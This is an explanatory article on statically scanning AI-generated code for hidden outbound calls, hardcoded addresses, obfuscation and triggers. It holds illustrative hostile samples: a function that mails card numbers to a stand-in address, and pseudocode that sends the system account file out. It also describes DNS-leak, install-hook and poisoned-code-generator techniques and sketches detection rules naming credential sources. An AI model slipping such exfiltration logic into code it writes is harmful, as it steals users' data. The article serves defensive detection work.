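# Scanning AI-Generated Code for Outbound Calls, Hardcoded Endpoints and Obfuscated Logic

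## Hidden behaviour in generated code and what a scan can ask

A code generator is a large language model, or an agent built on one, that writes program code on request. Beyond what the user asked for, the code may send data out of a system without the owner's consent (exfiltration), give an outsider access without the user's consent (a backdoor), or behave well until a condition is met, such as a particular date or machine name (a trigger). Static scanning looks for such behaviour in the program text without running it, while dynamic analysis runs the program and records what it does. Both rely on signals, which are observable features that make it more or less likely that the code is malicious. Examples include a network call, an address fixed in the code, and logic rewritten to make it hard to read (obfuscation).

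Hidden behaviour in code predates language models. In *A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples*, Landwehr, Bull and colleagues (1994) sorted 50 documented flaws by how they got into a program, first separating accidental flaws from deliberate ones because the remedies differ. They expected more code review and testing to reduce accidental flaws but to help much less against deliberate ones. Generated code complicates this distinction because a model can reproduce a scammer's address with no scammer involved in the exchange. A scan should therefore leave the question of intent until later, if it is considered at all, and first check what the code does beyond its declared purpose, meaning what the request, documentation or description says it should do.

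### Three questions about one function

Suppose a user asks for a function that takes a card number, asks the bank whether it accepts the card, and returns the answer. The code generator writes this:

```python
def authorize_card(number):
    """Ask the bank whether it accepts this card."""
    approved = bank.accepts(number)
    mail_card_number(number, "dev@example.com")
    return approved
```

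The example follows one in MITRE's *CWE-912*, the hidden functionality entry in the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a public catalogue of software and hardware weaknesses. The code does not run because it omits the helper that sends the mail.

The function is well written. It is short, its names are clear, and a comment explains it, so a style checker would report no problems.

A vulnerability scanner looks for accidental weaknesses that an attacker could exploit, and generated code often contains them. Livshits (2026), in *LLMs + Security = Trouble*, cites a study that found vulnerable code at rates between 9.8% and 42.1% across models. In *Secure and Functional Code Generation with Self-Evaluation* (2026), 29.2% of the samples that worked correctly still failed a security test. The scanner compares code with known kinds of mistake, such as a missing bounds check or outside text that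 reaches a database query unfiltered. The card function contains none of these mistakes, and it would also pass ordinary tests because it returns the right answer for every card.

It also mails every card number to a stranger. To notice this, one has to ask whether the code does something nobody asked for, and the answer depends on the request. Had the user wanted a copy sent to a fraud desk at that address, the same five lines would be correct. (They would be bad practice, and a scanner with a rule about private data leaving the program might flag the mailing line. It would flag it in both cases.)

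A specification usually lists only what a program must do. *Program Security* (2016), course notes from the University of Waterloo, gives the example of the Unix command that lists the files in a directory. Users wouldn't mind if the command also sorted the names, but they would object strongly if it also posted them to a public website. The notes advise reading every security-relevant specification as if it ended with "and nothing else", and raise the question of how to test for that. Ordinary tests tend to miss extra behaviour because they check for results that somebody thought of in advance.

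Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, turned the idea into a definition. They studied tools that language models call through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard under which the model sees a tool's description but not its code. Write F for what a tool does and E for the effects it has on its surroundings. Description and code are inconsistent when

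F(claimed) ≠ F(actual), or E(actual) ⊈ E(claimed).

A tool fails the first half if it does less or more than described, and the second half only if its code has an effect that the description omits. The card function passes the first half if we count only the answer it returns, but it fails the second. One example from Shi and colleagues is a tool that searches local files but also uploads the search query.

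Researchers checked 19,200 pairs of description and code from real servers and judged 9.93% of them inconsistent. In most of the inconsistent pairs, the description claimed more than the code did, and the causes include outdated documentation as well as deceit. Unexpected behaviour is not always malicious, so when a scan finds some, it is worth asking the user about.

Security specialists disagree on whether malicious code counts as a vulnerability. *A Software Flaw Taxonomy* repeats an objection to the 1994 scheme that if a system has a virus, the flaw is whatever defect let the virus in. MITRE does list malicious code in its catalogue, where *CWE-507* covers the Trojan horse, a product with useful functions and hidden code that violates the user's security policy. In the entry on non-replicating malicious code, MITRE suspects that ordinary weaknesses can often describe such code, but acknowledges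 that nobody has investigated this closely. The dispute matters in practice because rules that describe mistakes may not match code that works as its author intended. The Application Security Verification Standard, a checklist from the non-profit OWASP, has a separate requirement for unexpected behaviour, which applies at the upper two of its three levels. Reviewers must verify that source code and third-party libraries contain no unauthorised "phone home" or data collection.

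### How unwanted behaviour gets in

There are at least five routes, and not all of them need an attacker.

- A model can absorb malicious material in training, along with everything else on the open web. *Scam2Prompt* (2025) found production models writing malicious web addresses into code for ordinary requests.
- An attacker can plant examples in the training data on purpose, which is called poisoning. Improta (2025), in *Detecting Stealthy Data Poisoning Attacks in AI Code Generators*, studied a variant in which the attacker leaves a task's description alone and swaps its safe code for vulnerable code that does the same job.
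- An attacker can plant instructions in something the agent reads while it works, such as a file or a tool's description (prompt injection). *Beware EviLLM* (2026) describes a related attack through the user's account or browser.
- The generated code can be clean and still import a library that is not. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Cutting the Gordian Knot*, describe malicious uploads to the Python Package Index (PyPI), the public registry from which Python programmers install libraries, some of them under names that imitate legitimate packages.
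- An agent can step outside its task unprompted. Al Hasan and Biswas (2026), in *What Breaks When LLMs Code?*, confirmed 547 safety failures in user reports about coding models and tools, including an agent that edited a configuration file after its user had forbidden any change to existing code.

These routes leave different traces. A malicious dependency may show up in the generated text as a single import line. An agent that deletes a database may leave nothing in the code, because a command it ran did the damage. Improta's kind of poisoning produces a deliberate flaw that looks exactly like an accidental one, so a vulnerability scanner is the right tool for finding it.

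### From text to something a scanner can examine

A source file is a string of characters, which a scanner first splits into tokens, the smallest meaningful units, such as `approved`, `=` and `bank`. A search at this level can find the text "dev@example.com", but it can't distinguish an address in a comment from one in code that runs.

A parser then arranges the tokens into a syntax tree. The card function becomes a node with three main children below its comment (an assignment, a call and a return), and the call node has the card number and the address as its arguments. A rule can now match any call whose second argument is a fixed mail address, regardless of spacing and comments. Semgrep, a widely used scanner, matches such patterns directly on source code. Code generators produce many short, isolated snippets, and Improta chose Semgrep because it can handle them, whereas tools such as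 CodeQL often need to compile the code or infer its types.

The call graph records which functions call which. `authorize_card` calls `mail_card_number`, and if the scanner has the helper's source code, it can follow the call into it and find the library call that sends the mail. A static call graph is meant to cover every possible run, so it generally includes some calls that never happen.

Data-flow analysis traces whether a value from a source, where sensitive data enters the program, can reach a sink, where data can leave. In the example, `number` is the source, the mail call is the sink, and the path between them is one step long. Paths in real code pass through many variables and files.

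Guo and colleagues compare two packages to show what the trace adds. Both use the same two standard operations to encode data for a web address and turn bytes into plain text. The harmless package fetches an image from a server on the same machine and encodes it. The malicious one reads the system's file of user accounts, encodes it and sends it to an outside address. Three existing scanners flagged the harmless package, mainly because of a rule about suspicious links.

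He, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Do Skill Descriptions Tell the Truth?*, combined these layers in a tool called SkillScope. It checks "skills", small bundles of description and code that extend what a language model can do. The tool builds one graph from the syntax tree, the order in which statements can run, and the dependences between values. It marks every call that matches a keyword list, such as calls that read a stored password or post data to the web. It then follows the data and control edges from each marked call and records a link whenever it reaches another marked call. It skips the syntax tree's edges because unrelated calls can share a block of code. A language model then compares the marked calls and links with the skill's description.

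On a sample of 300 skills with 38 real mismatches, SkillScope found 36. It found only 30 when the language model was given the raw source code instead of the graph, and most of the extra misses involved a flow from one operation to another. The keyword list is the tool's weak point. Across the full set of 4,556 skills, SkillScope missed 15 mismatches, and 14 of them went through code that the list did not cover, such as software development kits or custom helpers similar to `mail_card_number`.

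### Counting a scanner's mistakes

SkillScope's results on the full set also define the error rates. Two of the researchers read all 4,556 skills without seeing the tool's verdicts, and their judgments serve as the ground truth.

| | Reviewers found a mismatch | Reviewers found none |
|---|---|---|
| Scanner flagged the skill | 413 | 74 |
| Scanner passed the skill | 15 | 4,054 |

An item is "bad" here if its code went beyond its description. He and colleagues did not try to judge intent. The scanner flagged 413 of the 428 bad items, a recall of 96.5%. Of the 487 items it flagged, 413 were bad, a precision of 84.8%. It also flagged 74 of the 4,128 harmless items, a false positive rate of 1.8%. That rate is different from the share of alarms that were false, which was 15.2% (74 of 487).

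Precision depends heavily on how common bad items are. In this collection they made up 9.4%. If the same scanner, with the same recall and false positive rate, were run on 100,000 functions of which 100 hid something, it would catch about 96 of them and flag about 1,800 harmless ones, so roughly one alarm in twenty would be real. The Waterloo notes make the same point with a breathalyser example and add that when most alarms are false, people usually overlook the true ones or switch the scanner off. A tool will therefore show much higher precision on a benchmark in which half the items are malicious, like the roughly 18,000 packages that Guo and colleagues assembled, than in daily use.

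### Why the measurements come from package registries

Computing any of these rates requires labelled items. Package registries can supply them because PyPI and npm (its counterpart for JavaScript) are public and very large, and malicious uploads leave a record that researchers can collect. For example, PyPI's staff confirmed 219 malicious packages that Guo and colleagues had found. Generated code, however, mostly goes from the model to one user's editor, where nobody labels it.

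The registry data contain many duplicates because attackers upload the same code in batches. Guo and colleagues' 8,543 malicious packages contained 2,283 distinct malicious snippets, so a scanner that recognises one popular snippet can look better than it is.

Findings about a package's code should carry over reasonably well to generated code, since code that sends a stolen password to an outside server looks much the same whoever wrote it. Findings that rely on a package's name or other metadata do not carry over, because a generated function has no such record. A scan can instead compare the function with the request that produced it. The request is a better guide to what behaviour is unexpected than anything in a registry, because it comes from the person who wants the code, while a package's description comes from its author, who may be the attacker.

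The request is still a loose standard, because people write short requests and leave most of what they want unsaid. *DevIntent* (Haing, Vidra and Setty, 2026) removed some constraints from the wording of 49 programming problems and kept them as hidden tests. Two models passed over 92% of the stated tests but broke the unstated constraints in 54.5% and 63.5% of cases. The constraints were removed deliberately, so these are not everyday rates, but they show how much a request can leave open. Reading a description too strictly also causes errors. Of SkillScope's 74 false alarms, 35 came from treating a detail, such as a particular file path, as a violation when the description already covered it in general terms.

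Researchers have begun to use the user's request when checking generated code. *WildCode Revisited* (2025) draws on real ChatGPT conversations, so the code can be read alongside what the user wanted. Livshits describes a system called Astrogator, which compares the code's effects with a formal version of the request that the user has confirmed. On 1,260 programs, it verified correct code in 83% of cases and caught incorrect code in 92%. Livshits doubts that this suits the people who most need it, since a developer who accepts every change without reading it is unlikely to study a formal version of the request.

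## Static signals: outbound calls, fixed addresses and concealed logic

Even a malicious program consists mostly of harmless lines. In *Unveiling Malicious Logic*, Ryan and Ifti (2025) examined 370 malicious Python packages statement by statement and marked 2,962 occurrences of malicious behaviour in 90,527 lines, roughly one for every 31 lines. They sorted these into 47 indicators of seven types. Many of the relevant statements, such as a server request, a decoding step or a file read, would look normal in any program. A scanner first has to find them, and then someone has to work out whether the task explains them.

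### Outbound calls

The simplest way to find outbound calls is to search for the names of library functions that open a connection, such as `requests.get` and `urllib.request.urlopen` in Python. But a program can call these functions by other names. After `import requests as r`, the call is `r.get(...)`, and after `from requests import get`, it is just `get(...)`, a name that many unrelated functions share. So the scanner first reads the import statements and builds a table that maps each local name to its full library name. It then visits every call in the syntax tree and looks up the name in the table.

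Guo and colleagues took this further in PyGuard, their detector for malicious Python packages. They used a language model to resolve renamed imports and nested calls, then replace each operation with a general description, so that a request through `urllib` and one through `requests` both counted as network communication. This reduced 13,834 operations to 327 categories. Three experts checked 500 snippets and found that the model had missed no operations, but that 174 of the 3,608 it listed were not in the code.

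A listed call may be inside a wrapper, such as `mail_card_number` in the card example, so the scanner marks every function that contains a listed call, then the functions that call those, and so on up the call graph. If a helper is in a library whose source code the scanner lacks, the helper's name must already be on the list, a requirement SkillScope did not fully meet.

CodeQL comes with much of this list built in. It stores a program's syntax tree, control flow and data flow in a database that analysts can query. Gobbi and Kinder (2024) used it in *GENIE* to search npm for malicious packages. Their simplest example query is a few lines long and returns every request a program makes through any supported library, along with its address. They point out that in Semgrep they would have had to write new patterns for each library.

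A program can also start another program to send data for it. The evidence is then inside a string, which the scanner has to parse as a shell command. Huang, Wang and colleagues (2024), in *DONAPI*, collected such commands from the scripts section of a package's manifest (the file that describes it), separate script files, and the arguments of functions that start a process. One npm package had all its malicious code in the manifest, so a scanner that reads only JavaScript would have missed it. The package's install command encoded the machine's hosts file, a local list of network names, and put the result in the path of a web address.

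A program can also leak data without making a web request. When it looks up a domain name, the query reaches a server that the domain's owner controls, so it can leak a value by including it in the name. Of the 125 previously unreported malicious packages that Gobbi and Kinder found on npm, 91 leaked data through such lookups and another 6 through ping, a command that tests whether a machine is reachable. A scanner that searched only for web functions could have missed these 97 packages, more than three quarters of the total.

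The hardest calls to find are those inside a dependency. Huang and colleagues start from the files that run when someone installs or imports a package. They replace each import statement with the code it refers to, rename anything that would clash, and repeat this two levels down. This produces a single file in which indirect calls become direct ones. Gobbi and Kinder analyse only the main package, so they cannot follow behaviour that an attacker has split across several packages. They say that including all dependencies would take a lot of resources, and their databases for 1.8 million packages already took up about 41 terabytes. A generated function is tiny by comparison, so following its imports should be practical.

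An outbound call alone is weak evidence of malicious code, since people often ask a code generator for programs that fetch the weather, charge a card or download a table. The call is more suspicious if sensitive data flows into it or if nothing in the user's request explains the destination. How the code handles the reply also matters, because a function that fetches something for its user normally does something with what comes back. Gobbi and Kinder print a simplified malicious package that posts the home directory, machine name and user name to the attacker's server, and handles both the reply and any errors with empty functions.

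Code that reports usage statistics is an exception, because it often ignores the reply too. Gobbi and Kinder found no clear npm policy on user tracking. After they reported 125 packages, npm replaced all but one, a tracker, with a security notice.

### Fixed addresses

To find fixed addresses, a scanner collects the string constants in the syntax tree, keeps those that look like a URL, domain or IP address, and splits each into its parts. The most important part is the host, which may be the same machine (`localhost`), a machine on a private network or a public server.

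Programs often build an address in stages, as the harmless package in Guo and colleagues' matched pair does. In simplified form:

```
server_address = "localhost:{port}"
req_url        = "http://{server_address}/view?{query}"
```

A scanner that checks one string at a time finds only fragments, because the first line lacks the form of a web address and the second has no host. Constant propagation solves this by carrying known values forward and leaving gaps for unknown ones, which gives `http://localhost:{port}/view?{query}`. The port and query remain unknown because they can change from run to run, but the host is certain, which is enough for this purpose.

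A program may never contact an address that appears in its source text. Links turn up in comments, licence notices, documentation and test data. XML files name their vocabularies with strings that look exactly like web addresses, but most programs never open them. *30 new Semgrep rules* (2024), from the security company Trail of Bits, gives an example of how plain text matching goes wrong. A file contains a system call and, above it, another that a programmer has commented out. Semgrep's Python mode reports only the live call, while its generic text mode can also match the commented-out one.

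Parsing removes comments, but documentation strings survive as ordinary constants, so searching the constants for addresses can also return links from documentation. Working backwards from the call is safer. Gobbi and Kinder's query for requests starts from each request and retrieves the text of its address, which leaves out links that no request uses. If the address comes from a configuration file, the query has no text to return, and the scanner can report only that the program contacts an unknown address.

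GuardDog, an open-source package scanner from the monitoring company Datadog, uses a cruder method. By default, it skips documentation formats such as Markdown and plain text, according to its project page, *GuardDog*. That should remove many false alarms. But it also skips JSON and YAML files by default. Programs often keep the addresses they contact in these files, and npm keeps its install commands in a JSON file. A scanner that skips these formats needs a separate check for the addresses and install commands.

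Once the scanner finds an address that the code contacts, it has to assess whether the address is suspicious. According to Datadog's *Finding malicious PyPI packages through static code analysis* (2022), the first version of GuardDog flagged link shorteners such as bit.ly and domains with endings common in malicious packages, such as .xyz and .top. Several of the malicious packages in the same article used none of these. One sent the machine's name to a general-purpose automation service, others sent stolen data to the chat platform Discord, and another downloaded its program from GitHub. Attackers can take advantage of a large service's good reputation for free. Raw IP addresses are also a common warning sign, but programmers often use them for test servers on their own machines.

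A more direct check for generated code is to see whether the address appears in the request or elsewhere in the user's project. If it appears in neither, the model supplied it. That may be fine, since models can supply correct addresses for many public services, but it's a good reason to ask the user about the address, even when a reputation service doesn't flag it.

### Concealed logic

Code can hide what it does by storing instructions as data and turning them back into code when it runs. In Python, `exec` and `eval` run a string as program text. A scanner treats them as sinks and traces where their arguments come from. If the path starts at a decoding function, the program is running code that a reader of the file can't see.

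Programs often decode base64, which writes arbitrary bytes with 64 printable characters, to handle e-mail attachments or embedded images, and notebooks and template engines run strings as code. Harmless programs have much less reason to decode a fixed string and then run it, because the author could have written the code out. GuardDog's first version had a rule for this pattern, and Datadog used it to find a package with an encoded string in the file that Python runs on import. The payload was hidden under several layers of encoding. Another package downloaded an ordinary-looking picture, extracted text from its pixels and executed it. A rule that lists only base64 decoders would miss that package, so it helps to start from `exec` and report any argument that the scanner can't resolve to visible text.

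A program that uses dynamic imports can choose a library by name at run time. Plug-in systems have good reason to do this, because the name depends on what the user has installed. It is stranger for a program to assemble the name from pieces when the name never varies. Constant propagation can often recover the full name, and the scanner then treats the result as a normal import.

Invisible characters can also hide code from a reviewer while leaving it readable to the computer. Unicode, the standard that numbers the characters of the world's scripts, includes characters with no width and others that change the direction in which an editor displays text. They can make a line of code look as if it does something different from what it does, or hide data in a string that looks empty. A scanner can easily find them by checking each character in a file against the relevant Unicode categories.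 They occur legitimately in Arabic and Hebrew text and in emoji that combine several symbols. They usually need no explanation in a string meant for display, but a long run of them in a string that the program decodes does.

Simple obfuscation of a whole file barely affects a syntax-based scanner. Minification, which strips spaces to make JavaScript files smaller, and variable renaming both leave the program's structure intact, and Gobbi and Kinder report that CodeQL handles both. Stronger tools stop CodeQL from tracing data properly. One popular obfuscator moves a program's strings into an array, shuffles the array, and retrieves each string by a computed position. The code that does this is easy to recognise, however, and Gobbi and Kinder wrote queries to detect the array, the code that parses numbers out of it, and the loop that shuffles it.

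In the whole npm snapshot, 376 packages matched all three. Gobbi and Kinder inspected 163 of them and found that all were obfuscated, but few appeared malicious. Most were small undocumented utilities whose authors seemed to want to stop others from copying them, and a few protected a paid product. The researchers still advise npm to ban obfuscated uploads because nobody can check them. Huang and colleagues likewise say that obfuscation does not prove malice, since developers also use it to save space or protect their work.

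I would expect this signal to be stronger in generated code.

A user who asks for a function gains nothing from unreadable code, and the usual reasons for obfuscating a finished product don't apply to a new draft.

### Entropy and its blind spots

Some scanners look for encoded or random-looking text by measuring its entropy. For a string in which each distinct character makes up a share *p* of the total, the entropy in bits per character is

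H = −Σ p log₂ p,

where the sum runs over the distinct characters. It is zero if all characters are the same and grows as the characters become more varied and more evenly spread.

Take the word "download". The letters d and o occur twice each, so *p* is 1/4 for both, and the other four letters have *p* = 1/8. Since log₂(1/4) = −2 and log₂(1/8) = −3,

H = 2 × (1/4 × 2) + 4 × (1/8 × 3) = 1 + 1.5 = 2.5 bits.

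The npm package with the hosts file sent its data to a domain whose first part is "l293fbwv". All eight characters differ, so H = 8 × (1/8 × 3) = 3 bits. This random-looking string scores higher than the previous example, as it should, but the word "keyboard" also scores exactly 3 because its eight letters all differ too.

The formula counts characters and ignores their order, so a word and any rearrangement of its letters get the same score. A string of *n* characters can't score more than log₂ *n*, which is 3 bits for eight characters. A scanner with a threshold of 4.5 bits therefore can't flag a string shorter than 23 characters, however random it is. Huang and colleagues use the entropy of a domain's longest subdomain as only one of several features, along with its length and its shares of vowels and consonants. Vowels distinguish the two strings here, since "keyboard" has three, not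 counting the y, and "l293fbwv" has none.

Measuring entropy also produces errors on longer strings. Hexadecimal text uses only 16 symbols, so it never exceeds 4 bits per character, and a program hidden in it can score about the same as ordinary English documentation. Base64 text can reach 6 bits. Compressed data encoded in Base64 comes close to that limit because compression removes repetition, and encrypted data does too, so an embedded icon and an encrypted payload can have nearly the same score. A reviewer can use high entropy to locate unreadable strings, but learns far more from what the program does with them, especially whether it passes them to `exec`.

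### Sensitive reads, install-time code and triggers

A scanner detects reads of sensitive data by using a list of sources: files that hold accounts or credentials, environment variables with names like `AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY` (a key to Amazon's cloud), browser profiles, and the clipboard. It reconstructs any paths that the code builds from pieces, then compares the list with the arguments of functions that read files and variables.

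Programs often have a legitimate reason to read a secret and send it over the network. Any program that uses a paid web service reads a key and sends the service some proof of it, and code generators write such programs every day. A rule that flags every path from a key to a request would flag them all. It is more useful to flag keys sent anywhere other than the company that issued them, such as an Amazon key in a request to a chat platform.

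It also matters when code runs. Python packages can replace the standard install command with their own, and npm packages can name a command that runs before installation. In Gobbi and Kinder's set of 75 removed malicious packages, 72 acted during installation. This is attractive to attackers because the code runs even if the victim never uses the package. Harmless packages also run install commands, for instance to compile a component for the user's machine. One of the patterns that Guo and colleagues found only in harmless code is handling file paths, running a shell command and exiting.

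A single generated function has no installer, although an agent that sets up a whole project may well write one. The closer parallel is code that runs on import. Huang and colleagues describe an npm package that, when imported, immediately sent the machine's name to an outside server and then ran a command to give that server control of the machine. In generated code, a scanner can list the statements outside any function and check them for network calls and sensitive reads, which someone who asked for a function would not expect to happen before they call it.

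Triggers are conditions too, and programs are full of conditions. The scanner goes through the branches in the syntax tree and picks out those that depend on the date, the machine's name, the user's name or similar facts about the surroundings. Data-flow analysis helps if the program stored the date in a variable earlier on. A harmless case looks like this:

```python
if date.today() > date(2027, 1, 1):
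    show_renewal_notice()
```

Code can have ordinary reasons to check the date or the machine it runs on, because licences expire and tests skip steps on machines that lack some component. The code inside the branch is therefore more informative than the condition. If a network call runs only on one named machine, there should be a reason for that in the task. Static scanning is useful here because it can examine a branch that a test run on the wrong day would never enter.

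### Why combinations work better

Guo and colleagues provide the best quantitative evidence of how signals combine. They turned code snippets into ordered lists of actions, 1,081 from malicious code and 1,350 from harmless code, and searched for recurring subsequences, allowing other actions in between. They kept the subsequences that occurred only in malicious code or only in harmless code, plus a few that were much more common in one than the other, then reduced these to the smallest set that still covered most of the lists.

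This produced 304 patterns, 86 of which occurred only in malicious code. Those 86 averaged 2.8 actions and together covered 948 of the 1,081 malicious lists. One of them began by reading an environment variable, then read the clipboard and wrote to it. A pattern from harmless code also began by reading an environment variable, but then started another program and read its output. The shared first step carries almost no information, so the clipboard steps distinguish the malicious pattern. Attackers do use the clipboard for theft. One package that Datadog found replaced any cryptocurrency address the user copied with the attacker's own.

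These coverage figures were measured on the same data the patterns came from, and a pattern could qualify with as few as two examples. "Only in malicious code" therefore applies only to this collection. The 192 patterns found only in harmless code covered just 60% of the harmless lists, presumably because harmless programs do a wider variety of things than malicious ones.

Version 2 of GuardDog listed every match of every rule, although Datadog's *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026) acknowledges that each rule was only a weak hint. Version 3 separates capability rules from threat rules. Capability rules describe what code can do, such as make outbound calls. Threat rules match suspicious details, such as the name of a sensitive file or a routine that undoes obfuscation. The scanner reports a risk when it finds a match of each kind, and lowers the severity if the matches are in different files.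 A network library doesn't meet this test because it matches only capability rules, and a test file may not meet it because it matches only threat rules.

It then computes a score from 0 to 10. The severity of the worst finding and the specificity of the matches to malware count for 30% each. The completeness of the attack, from first access to the removal of data, and the sophistication of the technique count for 20% each. In its announcement, Datadog doesn't derive these weights from data, so the score is better read as a ranking than as a probability.

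The same release replaced Semgrep with YARA, a tool that matches text and byte patterns and combines them with logical conditions. Datadog says it switched because Semgrep was slow and used a lot of memory on large packages, and because the old rules fitted known examples too closely to catch new ones. YARA is less precise about code structure, so two matches in the same file may be unrelated.

### Two packages that look alike

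The matched pair from Guo and colleagues, which the previous section described briefly, is a good test of all this. The harmless package is `gen_wrappers`, version 0.7.1, and the malicious one is `gmgeoip`, version 0.0.2. In pseudocode:

```
gen_wrappers
    query = url_encode(filename, subfolder, type)
    image = fetch from the image server on this machine, using query
    return base64(image)

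gmgeoip
    text = read the system's file of user accounts
    body = url_encode(base64(text))
    send body to a collection address on the public internet
```

A list of functions can't separate them, but several other things can:

| | `gen_wrappers` | `gmgeoip` |
|---|---|---|
| What it sends | A file name, folder and type that the caller supplied | The system's account file |
| Where it sends it | A server on the same machine | An outside address fixed in the code |
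| When it applies base64 | To the reply, after the call | To the file, before the call |
| What the call is for | It obtains the image that the function returns | It delivers the file, and the code discards the reply |

The destination is the easiest of these to check and perhaps the least reliable. If the image server moved to another company's data centre, `gen_wrappers` would contact an outside address and still be harmless. The source and purpose of the call would not change.

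Entropy would actually point the wrong way. A base64 version of a compressed image scores close to 6 bits, while the account file repeats the same words and separators on every line and should score lower even after encoding. (A static scanner would measure neither, since both strings exist only while the program runs.)

#### A pattern rule

GuardDog has treated such code in three ways over the years. Its rule for suspicious links, the kind that caused the false alarms on `gen_wrappers`, checks only the address.

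The first release also had a rule for stolen data, of which Datadog published a simplified version. It uses Semgrep's taint mode, a form of data-flow analysis that marks values from a source and follows the marks. As Semgrep's documentation explains, the marks travel through assignments and function calls, and the tool reports a finding if they reach a sink before the program has checked or cleaned the value. In words, the published rule is:

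```
source: the machine's name, or either of two Amazon key variables
sink:   any call to the requests library
report: a marked value that reaches the sink
```

This rule correctly passes `gen_wrappers`. It wrongly passes `gmgeoip` because its sources don't include the account file and its sinks don't include `urllib`, which the package uses to send its data. Adding both would fix this case. GuardDog shipped a fuller rule than the published one, but any such rule depends on its lists of sources and sinks.

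Version 3 should do better, judging by its design. Both packages can make outbound calls, but only `gmgeoip` also names a sensitive file, so only `gmgeoip` would match both a threat rule and a capability rule. However, the two rules only have to match in the same file, so a login tool that reads the account file and checks for updates fifty lines later could produce the same combination.

#### A data-flow query

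A CodeQL query requires an actual path. Gobbi and Kinder developed theirs by studying a known malicious package and describing its behaviour in general terms, which took them 30 to 45 minutes per group of similar packages on average. For the package that posts the user's details, the simplified query amounts to this:

```
source: the result of asking for the machine name, home directory or user details
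step:   storing a marked value in an object marks the whole object
sink:   whatever the program writes into the body of a request
report: every source and sink that a path connects
```

The extra step is necessary because the package puts the three values into an object and converts the object to text before sending it. Without the step, the query would stop tracking the values at the object. The simplified query would still match legitimate programs that, say, report the machine's name to a monitoring service, so the version the two researchers ran on the registry required all three values to reach the request. Their 12 queries produced no false alarms on npm, but the researchers acknowledge that avoiding false alarms probably meant missing some malicious packages.

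Their queries cover JavaScript, so the pair would need a Python equivalent, with a read of the account file as its source and the body of a web request as its sink. Gobbi and Kinder also recommend including the encoding step, by tracing one path from the source to the encoder and a second from the encoder to the sink. Both paths exist in `gmgeoip`, but neither exists in `gen_wrappers`, because that function never reads a sensitive file and encodes only what it receives.

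This result would no longer hold if the query treated every environment variable as sensitive and the address as a sink. Gobbi and Kinder list environment variables among the common sources in malicious packages, but `gen_wrappers` also reads one to find its image server's port, which becomes part of the address in the request. The query would therefore report a real path from source to sink in the harmless package. To avoid that, the analyst has to specify which variables are sensitive or exclude calls to the same machine.

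If a code generator had written these two functions, the user's request would help settle what the query leaves open. The name `gmgeoip` suggests a tool that finds the location of an IP address, and such a tool could reasonably contact an outside server. It would need to send the IP address, but not the list of user accounts.

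## What can be decided from program text alone

Longer lists of functions and better tracing would fix many of the mistakes scanners make, but not all of them. No method can correctly predict certain behaviors for every program, including whether it will ever open a connection.

### Why no scanner is always right

Suppose somebody had a scanner that always answered this question correctly. Take any program P that only calculates and never touches the network, and wrap it like this:

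```python
def wrapped():
    P()
    open_connection()
```

The second line runs only if P finishes. (If P can crash, the wrapper catches the error and carries on.) So `wrapped` opens a connection exactly when P halts, and a perfect scanner could be used to decide whether P halts. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can decide this for every program, which is known as the halting problem, so the perfect scanner can't exist.

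Rice proved a much more general version in *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems* (1953). No general method can decide, from a program, whether the set of values it can produce has a given property, unless all such sets have it or none do. The theorem covers our scanner if we count "opened a connection" as one of the values. It doesn't cover properties of the text itself, such as whether a file contains the word `requests`, so a scanner can still search for names and patterns.

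However, it is easier to confirm that a program does something than that it never does. Rice showed that one can list all the programs that produce a given value by running every program side by side and noting each one when the value appears. No such list is possible for the programs that never produce anything. In principle, then, a long enough run on the right input will confirm that a program opens a connection, but no general method can confirm that it never will, and a week of observation without a connection shows only that the program opened none that week.

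It doesn't help to accept only programs that are certain to finish. Rice found "the same unfortunate situation" there, even for primitive recursive functions, which are roughly what one can compute with loops whose length is fixed before they start. A small example shows the difficulty:

```python
def check(n):
    if finishes_within(P, n):    # run P for at most n steps
        open_connection()
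```

This function finishes for every n. Whether any n makes it open a connection is again the question of whether P halts.

Fred Cohen, who did some of the earliest research on computer viruses, found a more direct argument that doesn't involve halting. He defined a virus as a program that can infect other programs by changing them to include a copy of itself, possibly an altered one. In *Cure of Computer Viruses* (1984), he imagines a procedure D that always recognises a virus, and then a program that runs D on itself, infecting other programs if D classifies it as harmless and infecting nothing if D classifies it as a virus. D is wrong either way. The same argument applies to our scanner if we replace "infecting other programs" with "opening a connection".

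Cohen used the same argument to show that no procedure can always tell whether two variants of a program are equivalent, so a scanner with a complete record of known malicious code could still fail to recognise a rewritten copy. Watching a program's behaviour doesn't solve the problem either, because the system services that a virus uses also have legitimate uses, and a compiler that compiles a new version of itself counts as a virus under his definition.

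Cohen's self-contradicting program has to contain or call the scanner that is examining it, so a code generator is unlikely to produce it when asked for a sorting function. These proofs establish that every scanner fails on some programs, but not how often it will fail on the programs people actually ask for, which has to be measured.

### Wrong answers or no answer

A scanner that always answers yes or no must make infinitely many mistakes. If it made only finitely many, someone could store the correct answers to those cases in a table and have a perfect scanner, which is impossible.

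The designer can still choose which kind of mistake to make. A scanner that flags every program in which it can't rule out a connection will miss none, provided it knows all the operations that can open one, but it will raise false alarms. Reporting only proven connections avoids those false alarms, but some connections will be missed. In *Computer Viruses* (1987), Cohen considers flagging events that are rare in normal use to catch many viruses, while accepting both kinds of error. He adds that an attacker who knows the threshold for flagging can stay below it.

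The alternative is to let the scanner answer "unknown", so that it can be right whenever it answers yes or no. A scanner that always answered "unknown" would never be wrong either, so it also matters how much code the scanner leaves undecided and how that code will be checked, for example by a reviewer or in a test run without network access.

### Certifying restricted code

Rice noted that special methods will exist for particular functions. His impossibility result applies to a method that must handle every program, and a scanner doesn't have to accept every program.

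Cohen gives the example of a system whose only operation is to display a file. Such a system can't modify files, so no virus can spread on it. He thought this restriction might suit a fixed database or mail system, but certainly not software development. A single generated function is more promising because it often needs very few operations, even if the program around it needs many. The scanner can then check whether the function has any means of opening a connection, instead of trying to predict whether it will open one.

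#### No imports and no dynamic execution

```python
def running_total(values):
    total, result = 0, []
    for value in values:
        total = total + value
        result.append(total)
    return result
```

This function adds numbers and puts them in a list. Nothing in it can reach the network, and a scanner can confirm this by checking each operation against a list of permitted ones. The scanner doesn't need to work out whether the loop ends, because even if `values` never ran out, the function would run forever without opening a connection.

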